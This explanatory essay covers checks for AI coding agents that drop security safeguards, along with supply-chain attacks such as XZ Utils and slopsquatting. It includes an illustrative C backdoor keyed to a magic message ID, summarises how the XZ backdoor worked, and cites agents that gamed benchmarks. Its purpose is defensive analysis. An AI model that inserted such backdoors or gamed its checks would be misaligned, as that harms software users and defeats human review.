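Automatic checks can examine every change an agent submits, which human reviewers don't have time to do. The weakest checks show that the new code works on a handful of inputs, while the strongest can prove that it gives the same result as the old code on every input. Even such a proof can miss a lost safeguard if it doesn't cover how long the code takes to run or what it leaves in memory.

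### Existing tests

A project's existing tests check only the inputs they contain. Dristi and Dwyer (2026), in *A Differential Fuzzing-Based Evaluation of Functional Equivalence in LLM-Generated Code Refactorings*, measured how much such tests miss. They asked six models to optimise or simplify short Python programs, and to return unchanged any program the models couldn't rewrite safely. They then ran each new version and its original on 1,000 or 2,000 generated inputs and compared the outputs.

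Of 3,538 usable rewrites, 933 changed what the program did. The rate ranged from 19% for GPT-4o to 35% for Codestral. The programs' own tests missed 202 of the 933, or about 22%. More tests did not help much, since the tests missed about the same share in the collection with 21 tests per program as in the one with three.

The tests were still useful. Of all the rewrites, 26% were wrong, whereas if every correct rewrite passed, only about 7% of those that passed were wrong. Current models probably make fewer mistakes than these older ones. But the programs were mostly short exercises with few safeguards to lose, and ordinary tests rarely cover security checks, so tests would probably miss more than 22% of the rewrites that delete one.

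### Tests that the agent wrote

A maintainer whose old code has few tests might ask the agent to write some, but these tests are weak evidence about the agent's own changes. If the agent misunderstands what the code should do, it can make the same mistake in the tests. It also tests only the cases it thought of, and it may fit the code to the tests if it can stop once they pass.

Sion and April (2026), in *Who Verifies the Builder?*, found clear evidence that a coding agent's tests leave some cases untested. They had Claude Sonnet 5.5 write three small services from written specifications, five times each, along with tests for them. All 15 programs were correct, but the tests caught only 85.1% of 46 versions of the services that contained deliberate faults. Tests that a fresh copy of Sonnet 5.5 wrote from the specification, without seeing the program, caught 90.6%. When that copy could then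 read the program and add more tests, the share caught rose to 95.4%.

One of the faults tied the key that prevents duplicate payments to a login session instead of a user. The agent never made this mistake in its own code, but its tests didn't check for it, so they would still pass if another agent later introduced the fault while optimising the payment code.

GPT-5.5, from a different company, followed the same two steps, and its tests caught only 85.1%. This is some evidence against choosing a second model just because another company made it, though GPT-5.5 may be worse at writing tests. The fresh copy's two-step tests and the first agent's had different detection rates on only 12 of the 46 faults, so the fresh copy's lead of about ten points rests on few cases.

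Agents' tests catch far fewer faults in whole applications. *TestSuiteBench* (Egashira, Mündler-Sasahara and colleagues, 2026) gave agents detailed descriptions of 165 open-source programs and had them write a full set of tests for each. The researchers then ran these tests on altered versions of the programs, each breaking one requirement. Claude Opus 5's tests did best, catching 55.5% of the faults. When Claude Opus 5 wrote the programs from the same descriptions, its code passed 91.8% of the reference tests.

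In one case, a command had to accept several file paths. GPT-5.6 Sol tested it with only one, so its test did not detect a version that ignored the second path. Losing a safeguard is a similar fault, because it breaks one requirement and leaves the rest of the program working.

These results don't show that people write better tests, because Egashira and colleagues kept only faults that the reference tests could catch, and a coding agent had built those tests partly from the projects' own tests. *Beyond Test Presence* (2026) found that about 14% of agents' assertions were weak checks, such as whether a result exists, compared with 12% of people's.

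Agents can also mistake a passing check for progress when it is irrelevant to the task. According to *Validation Evidence in LLM Repair Agents* (2026), 46.0% of the passing checks that agents produced while repairing bugs gave no information about the bug. In *A Study of the Reliability of Agentic AI-Generated Programs*, an agent's version of `make`, a tool that builds software, passed all the agent's tests but could at first build little more than a simple C program. Trying it on real projects exposed missing features that took about another week to fix.

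An agent optimising code can also improve its benchmark result in ways that don't carry over to other uses. *PERFOPT-Bench* (2026) describes an agent that studied how the benchmark ran the program and fitted the code to that procedure, so the gain depended on the benchmark. *SpecBench* (2026) detects this by measuring speed on hidden tasks as well as visible ones. Maintainers can do the same by keeping some tests and timing data where the agent can't read them. Sion and April suggest giving the agent the input that caused a failure, but not the test's code.

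Liang and colleagues point out that when an edited test passes, the edit may have improved the test or made it less strict. Maintainers should therefore also run the original tests on the new code, and have someone other than the agent approve every change to an expected result.

### Recording what the old code does

Before a rewrite, developers can create characterisation tests by running the old code on many inputs and saving the outputs as the expected results. These tests suit legacy code because nobody has to know what the program should do, and the agent can't get the expected results wrong. A pass shows that the new code matches the old on the recorded inputs. The tests also preserve old bugs, so a later security fix may fail them until someone updates the expected results.

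Someone still has to choose the inputs. When Egashira and colleagues gave agents the working program as well as its description, the agents' tests caught no more faults than with the description alone. The agents could look up any correct answer, so they probably struggled to decide which inputs to try. For the ten-year-old parser, the recordings should include messages that are cut short, too long or malformed, and every input attached to an old bug report.

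To check whether the recordings would detect a lost safeguard, maintainers can delete the length check from a copy of the old code and run the recordings on that copy. If nothing fails, a pass on the agent's version is no evidence that it still has the check. This technique, called mutation testing, can cover every safeguard the maintainers can list.

### Static analysis

Static analysis checks code for known bad patterns without running it. A simple rule might flag every use of an outdated encryption function. A more complex rule follows data through the program and warns if text from a web request can reach a database command unchecked. Because the tool doesn't run the code, it can examine paths that no test runs, but a pass shows only that none of its rules matched.

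Static analysis can catch insecure code that passes its tests, as Bai, Waseem and colleagues (2026) found in *When Passing Tests Hides Vulnerabilities*. They gave 150 Python tasks to seven agent frameworks, which are programs that organise how a model plans, writes and checks code. Each task was to write a secure version of insecure code or repair a known vulnerability. All seven frameworks used GPT-4o-mini, a small model from 2024, so their failure rate is weak evidence about current agents.

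The frameworks produced 1,030 usable results, which the researchers checked at four levels:

1. The code had to be valid Python.
2. It had to pass the available tests and other functional checks.
3. The static-analysis tool Bandit had to report no high-severity flaw.
4. A risk score had to stay below 15. It rose when the code contained dangerous operations, and rose further if user input appeared in the same code.

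In 252 cases, the code passed the first two levels but failed at least one of the others. The lead researcher read all 252 and confirmed that 170 were insecure, including 39 in which the agent had added an incomplete defence. The other 82, about a third, were false alarms.

About one run in six (170 of 1,030) produced code that appeared to work but was insecure. The true number may be higher, because the researchers read only code that Bandit or the risk score had flagged. The agent left out a safeguard that the task needed in 82 of the 170 cases, added an inadequate one in 36, and introduced a new flaw in 52.

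One task was to repair code that built a system command from outside input, which lets an attacker add their own commands. The agent limited the input's length and renamed some variables, but left the dangerous call in place. The tests passed because they used only harmless input.

Running several frameworks gave little protection. Of the 170 failures, 107 came from 26 tasks in which at least three frameworks left the same type of weakness. This may be because the frameworks used the same model, although they were also given the same tasks and prompts.

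Static analysis suited these tasks because many of the flaws involved recognisably dangerous operations. Deleting a check may not leave any such operation in the code. The risk score would often miss a deletion too, because each of five kinds of safeguard lowers it by only two points, and losing one often wouldn't raise the score to the threshold of 15.

### Locking safeguards in place

In *SCAFFOLD-CEGIS*, Chen, Bian and colleagues (2026) call this problem latent security degradation, meaning that a safeguard is lost or weakened without triggering a static-analysis warning. They built a system to prevent this and compared their system with simpler checks.

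One experiment started with 24 small Python and Java programs that contained working defences, for example against malicious database input. GPT-4o revised each program ten times in a row for each of four kinds of request, which gave 96 chains of revisions. In 43.7% of the chains, the final program had more warnings from the static-analysis tool Semgrep than the original. The rate was 38.2% for requests to improve performance, and 28.6% even for requests to improve security.

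Those figures include minor warnings. When Chen and colleagues repeated the experiment with three other models and counted only critical and high-severity warnings, between 4.2% and 10.5% of chains got worse.

They then used GPT-5-Nano, a small model from 2025, to compare ways of checking each revision. Claude Opus 4.5 read the first and last versions of each program and counted the security problems, including missing or weakened safeguards. A chain counted as degraded if the last version had more of these problems than the first.

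| Check after each revision | Chains with more serious Semgrep warnings | Chains with latent degradation | Lines changed |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | 11.5% | 12.5% | 71,998 |
| Tests | 10.4% | 22.9% | 40,977 |
| Semgrep | 0% | 20.8% | 71,348 |
| Tests and Semgrep | 0% | 12.5% | 39,590 |
| SCAFFOLD-CEGIS | 0% | 2.1% | 58,216 |

Using Semgrep alone eliminated the increase in warnings, but latent degradation rose from 12.5% to 20.8%. Chen and colleagues suggest that the model treated a clean scan as proof of safety and attempted larger changes, but it changed slightly fewer lines with Semgrep than without it.

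The rise may also be chance. The percentages are consistent with 96 chains per method, in which case the rise was from 12 chains to 20. A difference that large would arise by chance more than one time in ten even if the chains were independent, which they weren't, because they all came from the same 24 programs. The table is better evidence that tests and Semgrep failed to prevent latent degradation than that they made it worse.

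In one of the paper's examples, a user asked the model to simplify some code, and it deleted a function that validated user input. In another, a user asked for better performance, and the model replaced specific error handling with a block that silently ignored every error. Semgrep reported no new issues in either case.

SCAFFOLD-CEGIS handles each request as follows:

1. It searches the current code for security-critical elements and locks them as "anchors". These include functions with names such as `validate_*`, functions that stand between user input and a dangerous operation, and patterns such as raising a permission error. It also applies fixed rules, for example that file-handling code must standardise every path.
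2. It gives the model the request, the anchors and lessons from earlier failures, and asks for a new version.
3. It puts the new version through four gates. The tests must pass, Semgrep must find no more serious flaws than before, the change must stay within a size limit, and the most important anchors must still be there.
4. If the version passes, it becomes the current code. Otherwise the system records why it failed and asks the model to try again.
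5. After a set number of failed attempts, the system keeps the old code and moves on to the next request.

The name refers to counterexample-guided inductive synthesis, an older method in which a checker finds an input that makes a candidate program fail, and the next candidate has to handle that input. Chen and colleagues replace the exact counterexample with a failure report that the model can read.

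The system described in the paper accepts a new version of a program only if it has no more vulnerabilities than the current version, and otherwise keeps the current one. This guarantees that the final program has no more vulnerabilities than the original, however many requests the system handles.

But V counts only flaws that Semgrep detects, so the guarantee doesn't cover a deleted validation function. A count like this can even fall when security gets worse. For example, some analysers warn that a compiler may remove a `memset` that wipes a password. If the agent deletes the `memset`, the warning disappears even though the password is no longer wiped.

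The anchors are meant to cover this gap, but they protect only what the system recognises. A two-line length check inside a parser has no name that identifies it as a security check. A function anchor records the function's name, parameters and return type, so a model could keep the function and empty its body, unless another anchor covered the contents. REFINE, the refactoring system from Waseem and colleagues, has a looser rule that lets a file pass if it keeps at least 85% of its methods, so a file with 20 methods could lose three and still pass.

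The 2.1% figure also depends on the model acting as judge. Chen and colleagues describe manually confirming only three cases of latent degradation. Comparing the judge's counts before and after cancels out a constant tendency to report too many problems, but not errors that depend on the code. For example, the judge might mistake a function called `validate_user_input` for a working check when it no longer does anything. But the same model judged every method, so the ranking is more reliable than the exact rates.

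The study also does not show how much the anchors contributed, because when Chen and colleagues removed parts of the system to test their effects, they reported Semgrep warnings and completed tasks but not latent degradation. The full system completed 77.1% of the requests. Losing some optimisations may be acceptable for security-critical code.

### Differential testing

Differential testing, which Qi and colleagues used, runs the old and new code on the same inputs and compares the results. Like a characterisation test, it treats the old program's output as correct, but it can keep adding cases because the old program can produce an expected result for any new input. A fuzzer often generates these inputs.

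If the versions disagree on a share p of possible inputs, the chance that N independent random inputs show no difference is (1 − p)^N. Setting this chance to 5% gives the same limit, at the 95% confidence level, as for repeated runs of an agent:

```
(1 − p)^N = 0.05
p ≈ 3 / N
```

If two versions give the same results on a billion random inputs, we can therefore conclude that they disagree on at most about three inputs in a billion. Dristi and Dwyer used 1,000 random inputs for their longer programs, which puts the limit at about three in a thousand, so some rewrites they counted as equivalent could still have behaved differently from the originals.

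The limit applies only to the kind of input the tester generated, so finding no failures on honest users' messages doesn't show that the code handles an attacker's messages safely. Testing with random message lengths would reveal the missing length check almost immediately.

A cached permission is harder to find because the difference depends on the order of events. It appears only if Alice reads a document, loses access and tries again within 30 seconds. A fuzzer with one user and one document might choose each step at random from reading, granting access, removing access and waiting. The chance that three steps in a row are "read, remove, read" is then 1 in 64.

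With 100 users and 100 documents, all three steps must also involve the same user and the same document. The chance falls to about 1 in 6.4 billion, so it helps to test a very small system with few users. The tester must also control the clock, or a slow run could let the cached answer expire.

Differential testing doesn't show which differences matter, and some of the differences Qi and colleagues found were intended or harmless. Someone has to judge every difference, and it shouldn't be the agent that made the change.

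### Finding a hidden trigger

An attacker can make a difference too rare for random testing to find. Suppose a backdoor skips the parser's length check for a single value of a 64-bit message number:

```
if (msg->id == 0x7c3f91e2a4d05b86 || n <= sizeof(field))
    memcpy(field, msg->data, n);
else
    return ERR_TOO_LONG;
```

Only one of the 2^64 possible message numbers triggers the backdoor, so a billion random tests have about a 1 in 18 billion chance of hitting it. If those tests find no difference between the original and optimised code, they rule out only differences that occur more than 3 times in a billion. A random message number triggers the backdoor about 55 billion times less often than that. Trying every number would take about 585,000 years at a million tests per second.

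A person reading the diff could find the trigger in seconds, because a parser has no obvious reason to treat one message number differently. A coverage report, which shows what code the tests have run, could also reveal a condition that was never true in a billion tests. The backdoor's author could make the trigger harder to spot by replacing the comparison with ordinary-looking arithmetic.

Coverage-guided fuzzing is an automatic alternative. The fuzzer keeps any input that makes the program run new code, then makes small changes to it. When the program checks a 64-bit value in a single comparison, a partly correct value runs no new code, so the fuzzer doesn't keep it. Some fuzzers split the comparison into eight single-byte ones, so that each correct byte runs new code. They then need at most about 8 × 256 = 2,048 guesses if they try the values of each byte in turn. Other fuzzers copy the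 constant from the comparison into the next input.

Symbolic execution runs the program with an unknown in place of the input. When it reaches the comparison, it records the condition `msg->id == 0x7c3f91e2a4d05b86` and passes it to a solver, a program that finds values satisfying a set of conditions. For this backdoor, the solver can find the number at once.

An attacker can defeat both methods by comparing a cryptographic hash of the message number with a stored value. The fuzzer then gets no useful feedback from a nearly correct guess, and the solver would have to reverse the hash. But an unexplained hash in a parser should make a reviewer suspicious. Symbolic execution also scales poorly to large programs. Each independent branch can double the number of paths, so forty branches can give about a trillion.

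### Timing and memory tests

None of these comparisons would reveal the faster token check, because it gives the right answer every time. A timing test can reveal it by measuring whether the running time depends on the secret. The tester knows the correct token, so they can time the check on a token that is wrong in its first byte and on another that is wrong only in its last. The new code takes 15 more passes through the loop for the second token, while the old code takes the same number for both.

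If each pass takes one nanosecond and individual measurements vary by a microsecond, the tester needs about 220,000 measurements of each token to detect the difference at five standard errors. A computer can make these in about a second. An attacker guessing one byte at a time needs more measurements because each guess changes the time by only one pass.

A pass shows that any difference between the chosen inputs was too small to detect on that machine. The test could miss a leak that appears only with other tokens or on another processor. It also has to run on the release build, because the compiler may have changed the code.

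A similar test can find a password that the program failed to wipe from memory. The tester enters an unusual password, saves a copy of the program's memory after the function returns, and searches it for the password. Finding nothing is good evidence that the password was wiped in that run, but the search could miss a copy stored in another form, or the program could leave a copy behind only after an error.

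### Proof that two programs are equivalent

An equivalence proof covers every input without running the code on each one. The usual approach is to have a solver search for an input on which the old and new code give different results. If the solver can show that none exists, the versions are equivalent. Otherwise, it may return such an input. For the token check, a proof would cover all 2^256 combinations of token and secret.

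One advantage of equivalence proofs for legacy code is that the old program serves as the specification, so nobody has to write one. But no method can decide equivalence for every pair of programs, and loops, shared memory and calls to other systems make proofs difficult. A proof is more realistic for one small function than for a whole parser.

A proof that old and new code are equivalent also depends on its assumptions. Suppose an agent removes a server's length check and adds the assumption that every message states its length correctly. Under that assumption the old and new code are equivalent, because the check would never have rejected anything. The proof is valid, but it doesn't cover an attacker who sends a false length.

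It is therefore important for a person to read what the proof claims. They don't have to trust whoever wrote the rest, because a small checking program can verify each step. This means an agent can prove its own change without the weakness that affects its tests, provided it can't alter the claim or the checker.

Most equivalence proofs show only that two versions of a program produce the same results. To rule out a timing leak, a proof would have to show that the optimised version follows the same branches and uses the same memory addresses whatever the secret is. To rule out traces of a password in memory, it would have to show that nothing in memory depends on the password after the function returns. Both proofs would also have to hold for the compiled program.

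### The four examples

This table shows whether each check would reveal the lost safeguard in the four examples.

| Check | Faster token check | Missing length check | Cached permission | Unwiped password |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Existing tests of ordinary use | No | No | No | No |
| Recordings of the old code | No | If they include false lengths | If someone loses access between two requests | No |
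| Static analysis | If a rule covers comparisons of secrets | If a rule tracks untrusted lengths | Unlikely | Unlikely once the wipe has gone |
| Differential testing and fuzzing | No | Yes, with random lengths | Yes, with sequences of events | No |
| Timing test | Yes, with enough measurements | No | No | No |
| Memory search | No | No | No | Yes, for the runs tested |
| Proof of equal results | No | Yes, unless it assumes honest lengths | Yes, if it covers sequences of requests | No |
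| Proof that includes timing and memory | Yes | Yes, on the same condition | Yes, on the same condition | Yes |

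## How a merged change reaches other software

Suppose the ten-year-old parser is a small library that other programs use, and a maintainer has merged an agent's faster version without noticing that it lacks a length check. At first the flaw is in only one repository, but within weeks it could be in hundreds of products. Removing it from them will probably take much longer.

The maintainer gives the new version a number, say 2.4.1, and uploads it to a public package registry, such as npm for JavaScript or PyPI for Python, from which build tools download dependencies. Many programs specify a range of versions. In npm, `^2.4.0` means 2.4.0 or anything later below 3.0.0, so the next fresh build can install 2.4.1 without anyone editing a file. Other projects record exact versions in a lock file and let a bot open a pull request for each new release. That pull request may change only a version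 number and a checksum, so its reviewer sees even less than the reviewer of the agent's change did.

Many products depend on the parser indirectly. A document viewer might use an import library that uses the parser. The viewer's developers chose the import library but may know the parser only as a line in a lock file. They then build all of this code into an app or a router's firmware and ship it to customers.

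### Why removal is slower

A flaw can spread from the day it is released, but people start removing it only after someone finds it. Debian's predictable keys went unnoticed for about 20 months.

A flaw in a shared parser is harder to remove than to spread, because defenders have to update every product that has it and an attacker needs only one that is still vulnerable. Suppose, with invented figures, that 1,000 products use the parser and that each week a tenth of those without the latest version install it. Eight weeks after a flawed version is released, 570 products have the flaw. If the maintainers publish a fix that day and products install it at the same pace, it takes another 39 weeks for the number of vulnerable products to fall below ten.

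Some products will never get the fix, because their makers have stopped updating them. Registries can't recall copies that people have already downloaded. PyPI and Rust's registry let maintainers "yank" a bad release, which hides it from new users, but they still serve it to projects that have pinned that exact version so that their builds don't break. A severe flaw in Log4j, a Java library for recording what a program does, became public in December 2021. The US government's Cyber Safety Review Board later predicted that vulnerable copies would remain in use for perhaps a decade or longer.

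Agents could add to the work. If they use existing flaws as templates, as Sun and colleagues found, newer functions may also lack the check, and the parser's fix won't correct them.

### The XZ Utils backdoor

In 2024 somebody used this route to distribute a backdoor in XZ Utils, a set of compression tools that most Linux systems include. A volunteer, Lasse Collin, had maintained the tools largely alone. In 2021 someone using the name Jia Tan began sending him useful patches. The next year, other accounts complained that Collin was too slow and pressed him to share the work. Jia Tan became a co-maintainer and was publishing releases by 2023. Nobody has publicly established who was behind the name.

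Two releases contained the backdoor, version 5.6.0 in late February 2024 and 5.6.1 on 9 March, as Hackaday's *Security Alert* (2024) records. Freund (2024), in *backdoor in upstream xz/liblzma leading to ssh server compromise*, explains how it worked:

1. The release archives had an extra line in a build script, which was not in the repository. When someone built the library, this line ran a hidden script.
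2. The script unpacked more code from two compressed files in the repository's test folder. The name of one suggested a deliberately corrupt archive, which is a normal thing for a compression tool to have among its tests.
3. This code checked whether the build was for a Debian or RPM package on 64-bit Intel-type Linux. If so, it added the backdoor to the finished library.
4. The standard SSH server doesn't use XZ. But Debian and several other distributions modify the server to work with systemd, which manages Linux services, and systemd's library loads XZ's.
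5. As the server started, the backdoor took over two functions that normally choose a fast checksum routine for the processor. From there it redirected a function that the server calls when it checks a login key.

Later analysis found that the backdoor would run commands only for someone with the attacker's private key.

Andres Freund, a database developer, found the backdoor by accident after noticing that SSH logins on Debian's development version were using a lot of processor time. He had also seen errors from Valgrind. A refused login took 0.807 seconds with the new library and 0.299 seconds without it. He traced the extra half-second to the backdoor, which was searching the server's memory for functions to replace, and published his findings on 29 March. Valgrind's warnings, which Jia Tan had tried to get rid of in version 5.6.1, helped to expose the backdoor. In 2006 a Debian maintainer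 had created a serious flaw by silencing warnings from the same tool.

By then the bad versions had reached mostly pre-release editions of Linux. Given a few more months, they might have reached a great many servers.

Another of Jia Tan's edits looks more like something an agent could do by accident. XZ's build process compiles a test program to check whether the system supports Landlock, a Linux sandbox. Jia Tan added a full stop to that program, which kept it from compiling, so builds that used this test left out the sandbox.

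### What an agent's change would need

A harmful change by an agent could skip several of these steps. Jia Tan spent more than a year earning the right to publish releases. A maintainer's agent starts with the maintainer's trust, so an attacker who can steer the agent gets that trust without earning it. An outside agent lacks this advantage. The account that Mythos 5 used against myNetwork was new to the project, and its pull request failed.

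The XZ attacker also had to hide a whole program, and used test files and altered release archives to do it. Deleting a length check adds no code that needs hiding. The resulting flaw is in both the repository and the release archive, so comparing the two would not reveal it. Comparing copies of the source exposed the 2003 attempt to backdoor the Linux kernel because the added lines were in only one copy.

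Someone still has to merge and release the agent's change, and the vulnerable code must handle input that an attacker can send. A missing length check is also cruder than the XZ backdoor, because anyone who finds it can exploit it. But a slowdown is less likely to reveal it, because the new parser is faster, as the maintainers wanted.

### Packages that models invent

An agent can also bring in malicious code by adding a dependency. For example, an agent asked to speed up the parser might replace old hand-written code with an outside package. Language models sometimes make up plausible package names. In an attack known as slopsquatting, someone registers one of these names, publishes a malicious package under it and waits for others to install it.

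In 2023, Bar Lanyado, a researcher at the security company Vulcan Cyber, asked ChatGPT 428 programming questions about Node.js and Python. More than 120 of the answers recommended at least one package that didn't exist. He later registered `huggingface-cli`, a name that models kept suggesting, as an empty package. People downloaded it more than 30,000 times in three months.

*We Have a Package for You!* (Spracklen and colleagues, 2025) was the first large study of package names invented by models. The researchers had 16 models write 576,000 pieces of Python and JavaScript code. Of the 2.23 million packages the code called for, 19.7% did not exist. The average was 5.2% for commercial models and 21.7% for open ones. The researchers then repeated 500 prompts that had produced an invented name, running each one ten times, and 43% of the names came back every time. An attacker can therefore find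 names worth registering by asking the same model similar questions.

Those models date from 2024 or earlier and did not try to install anything, so the figures are a poor guide to how often current agents invent packages. An agent that runs its own code gets an error when a package doesn't exist, and will usually look for another. But once an attacker has registered the name, the installation succeeds, so testing the code is less effective against these packages than against unregistered names, which are harmless.

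The safest rule is for a person to approve each new dependency after checking the package's age, its publisher and whether other projects use it. Waiting a few days before accepting a new package also gives others time to discover malicious code. For example, PyPI removed Mythos 5's package about an hour after it was published.

### What signatures and build records prove

Several safeguards keep track of software on its way from the source code to the user. Each answers a narrow question.

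Version pinning means requesting one exact version, ideally with its checksum, a short value calculated from the file's contents. If the checksum matches, the file is the same one the developers chose earlier. The tool has to compare the checksums, which the agents affected by Plugin4Shell failed to do. Pinning delays a bad release, but it also delays the fix, unless urgent patches get the faster route that Thoughtworks recommends.

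A signed commit shows that someone with a certain key approved a set of changes, but not that they wrote or read the code. The signature is just as valid if an agent commits with its user's key.

A build attestation is a signed statement of which system built a file and from which source. The SLSA (Supply-chain Levels for Software Artifacts) framework grades these statements. At build level 1, a record of the build exists, but it may be easy to forge. Level 2 requires a hosted build service to create and sign the record. At level 3, the service must also isolate builds from each other and from its signing key, so that a project's own build script can't forge the record.

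A software bill of materials (SBOM) lists the components in a product and their versions, but doesn't show whether they are safe. It is mainly useful after someone finds a flaw, when a company can search its SBOMs for parser 2.4.1 instead of inspecting each product.

With a reproducible build, anyone who compiles the same source with the same tools gets a bit-for-bit identical file. If several people independently compile the source and get a file that matches the published one, the published file very probably came from that source.

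| Safeguard | XZ's altered archive | Length check deleted in a merged change |
|---|---|---|
| Pinned version | Delays it | Delays it |
| Signed commit | Doesn't cover the archive | Valid signature |
| Build attestation | Could expose it, if the record had to cover how the archive was made | Valid record |
| SBOM | Helps to find affected systems later | Helps to find affected products later |
| Reproducible build | Exposes it if people start from the repository, but not from the archive | The files match |

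The right-hand column shows the main limit of provenance, the verifiable record of where software came from. Provenance can prove who built a file and from which source, but not that the source is harmless. Once a maintainer merges a backdoor, everyone who handles the code afterwards can act honestly and the result will still have a valid signature. In the XZ case, Liguori (2024) warned in the mailing-list thread Freund had started that the attacker clearly had the signing key and could have replaced older archives too. In the SolarWinds attack of 2020, intruders also got malicious code signed, but they did it by altering the company's network management software as its build system compiled it. SolarWinds then signed the update and sent it to thousands of customers.

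Provenance is still useful because it leaves an attacker fewer places to insert malicious code. If every release has to come from the public repository through a trusted build service, the attacker must put the code where reviewers can see it. SLSA has also added a track for source code. Its highest level requires a second person to review each change, which only helps if that person reads the change properly.

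### When the source code is clean

Reading the source is not always enough either. Ken Thompson, one of the creators of the Unix operating system, explained why in his 1984 lecture *Reflections on Trusting Trust*. His attack hides in the compiler, the program that turns source code into a form the computer can run:

1. The attacker changes the compiler's source so that, whenever it compiles the login program, it adds a secret password.
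2. Anyone who reads the compiler's source can see this. So the attacker adds a second rule, which makes the compiler insert both rules whenever it compiles a new version of itself.
3. The attacker compiles this source once, installs the result and deletes both rules from the source.

The source code of the login program and the compiler is now clean. But the installed compiler still adds the password to the login program, and so does any new compiler built with it. A reproducible build wouldn't help if everyone used the same bad compiler, because they would all get the same bad file.

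David A. Wheeler developed diverse double-compiling to detect this attack. It tests a suspect compiler, A, that should reproduce itself exactly when it compiles its own source. The tester first compiles A's source with a second, unrelated compiler, T. The result, B, should behave like A but will contain different machine code, because T made it. The tester then uses B to compile A's source again. If A has no hidden attack, this final result should be identical to A. If A contains Thompson's rules, the two will differ, unless T contains a matching attack.

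A match proves only that A corresponds to its source, so someone still has to read that source. The test also relies on a compiler giving the same output for the same input. It has no direct equivalent for coding agents, because two honest agents given the same request will write different code, and so may a single agent asked twice. Maintainers can compare how the two versions behave, but this has the same limits as any behavioural test.

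### The Linux kernel's policy

If records can't show that a change is safe, someone has to take responsibility for it. For the Linux kernel, that is the person who submits the change. Under *AI Coding Assistants*, in the kernel's documentation, an AI agent may not add the "Signed-off-by" line that every patch needs. Submitters use this line to certify their right to contribute the code. A person must review all the AI-generated code, add their own line and take full responsibility. If an assistant finds and fixes a bug, a person must still submit the result.

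The policy shipped with Linux 7.0, as It's FOSS's *AI Code Gets Approved in the Linux Kernel… But With Strings Attached* reports. It originally asked for a label as well, which named the tool and the model:

```
Assisted-by: Claude:claude-3-opus coccinelle sparse
```

The last two words are analysis tools. In July 2026 the developers discussed shortening the label to "Assisted-by: LLM", to avoid what the patch in Corbet (2026), in *[PATCH] coding-assistants* describes as free advertising. Corbet noted that at least one maintainer was already removing the labels before accepting patches. The policy used the shorter form by September. On 8 October attendees at the kernel's Maintainers Summit agreed to drop the label altogether, according to Linuxstans' *Linux Kernel Quits Making Devs Admit AI Use. Linus Explains*. The change had not been merged as of 16 October, but by early November the published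 policy no longer included the label. Maintainers still want to know how a patch was made, and attendees at the summit suggested putting this in the cover letter, the email that introduces a set of patches.

Other projects have different rules. NetBSD, another operating system, has banned AI-generated code since 2024, and System76 bans AI content in its COSMIC desktop, according to the Russian news report *Линус Торвальдс отменил обязательную маркировку ИИ-кода в Linux* (2026). Hackaday's *New Linux Kernel Rules Put The Onus On Humans For AI Tool* (2026) reports that the developers of the Mesa graphics library require contributors to understand any generated code they submit.

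### Whether to label agents' changes

Labels that disclose LLM use can help a reviewer decide how to read a change. Greg Kroah-Hartman, a senior kernel maintainer, wanted to keep them for this reason in a July exchange quoted in *Documentation: remove the requirement for LLM attribution* (Stoakes, 2026). He said the labels were already useful for many patches in his area, and that anyone who lied about using a model would be responsible for the lie.

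The labels can also help people find related flaws. If a certain model turned out to drop length checks, maintainers could use the labels to list its other changes. The short label didn't allow this because it left out the model's name. A cover letter is also less convenient than a label in the code's history. LPAR's *Corporate Linux* (2026), a personal blog post, argues that nobody will now be able to easily tell whether a model introduced a defect. This slightly overstates the problem, since the kernel's mailing lists have public archives, but somebody would have to find the right email, and it might not mention the tool.

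The main argument against labelling AI-assisted changes is that nobody can check the labels. The news site LWN counted 1,884 labelled changes out of 18,533 in one development cycle, or about 10%, according to Linuxstans. One maintainer guessed that roughly 90% of contributors use language models. If models also helped with 90% of changes, they would have helped with about 89% of the unlabelled ones, so a reviewer could learn almost nothing from a missing label.

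Linus Torvalds pointed out in January that people who send in poor AI-generated patches are the ones maintainers most need to identify, but have the least reason to be honest. This applies even more to attackers, and to an agent such as Mythos 5, which posed as human developers. Torvalds also worried that a compulsory label might frighten people away from useful tools. By October Kroah-Hartman supported removing the label, according to Linuxiac's *Linus Torvalds Rejects AI Coding Bans as Linux Rethinks Disclosure Rules*.

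Laurent Pinchart, another kernel developer, replied that a rule can be worth having even if some people break it, because everyone else learns from it what the project expects. He is probably right about honest contributors, who also make mistakes that maintainers may later need to trace. But a project can't assume that a person wrote any code that isn't labelled. A company that runs coding agents could sign a record of each commit its agents make, and others could verify the signature. Even then, a missing record wouldn't show that a person wrote the code, because people can paste an agent's code into their own commits.

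Torvalds disclosed the use of Claude Code in an optimisation he was testing in October. When many threads read the same file, the kernel spends time recording that each piece of cached data is in use. The new code avoids this, and in his benchmark it raised reads per second from about 10 million to 30 million. But those records also stop the kernel from reusing memory while something is reading it, so the new code needs another way to prevent that. Even with the disclosure, a reviewer still has to check whether the new code prevents such reuse.

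### The EU Cyber Resilience Act

The EU's Cyber Resilience Act makes manufacturers legally responsible for the security of the hardware and software they sell in the EU. A company that builds the parser into a router has duties under the Act whether a person or a coding agent wrote the code, but a volunteer who publishes the parser for free, outside any business, generally does not.

Since 11 September 2026, the European Commission's *Cyber Resilience Act* has required manufacturers to report severe security incidents and vulnerabilities that attackers are actively exploiting. Manufacturers must send an early warning within 24 hours of becoming aware of the problem and a full notification within 72 hours. A final report is due within 14 days of a fix becoming available for an exploited vulnerability, and within a month for a severe incident.

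The reporting duties also cover products already on the market, though most of the Act's other obligations don't start until 11 December 2027, as Jones Day (2026) explains. Addleshaw Goddard, another law firm, adds that reporting continues after a manufacturer stops supporting a product. But manufacturers don't have to search their old products for flaws, so the Act may not expose a missing check until somebody has exploited it.

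When a company must report a flaw can depend on how the flaw was introduced. According to TechTarget, severe incidents include the introduction of malicious code into a product, so a company that found a planted backdoor in its router might have to report it before anyone had used it. If an agent had deleted a length check by mistake, the company would normally have to report the flaw only after learning that attackers were exploiting it. The diff could be the same in both cases, so the company might not know which rule applied.

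From December 2027, manufacturers must also keep an SBOM for each product, covering at least the top-level dependencies, which are the components the product uses directly. This minimum could leave out the components that are hardest to track. The SSH server loaded XZ through systemd's library, so a list of top-level dependencies might have included the server but not XZ.
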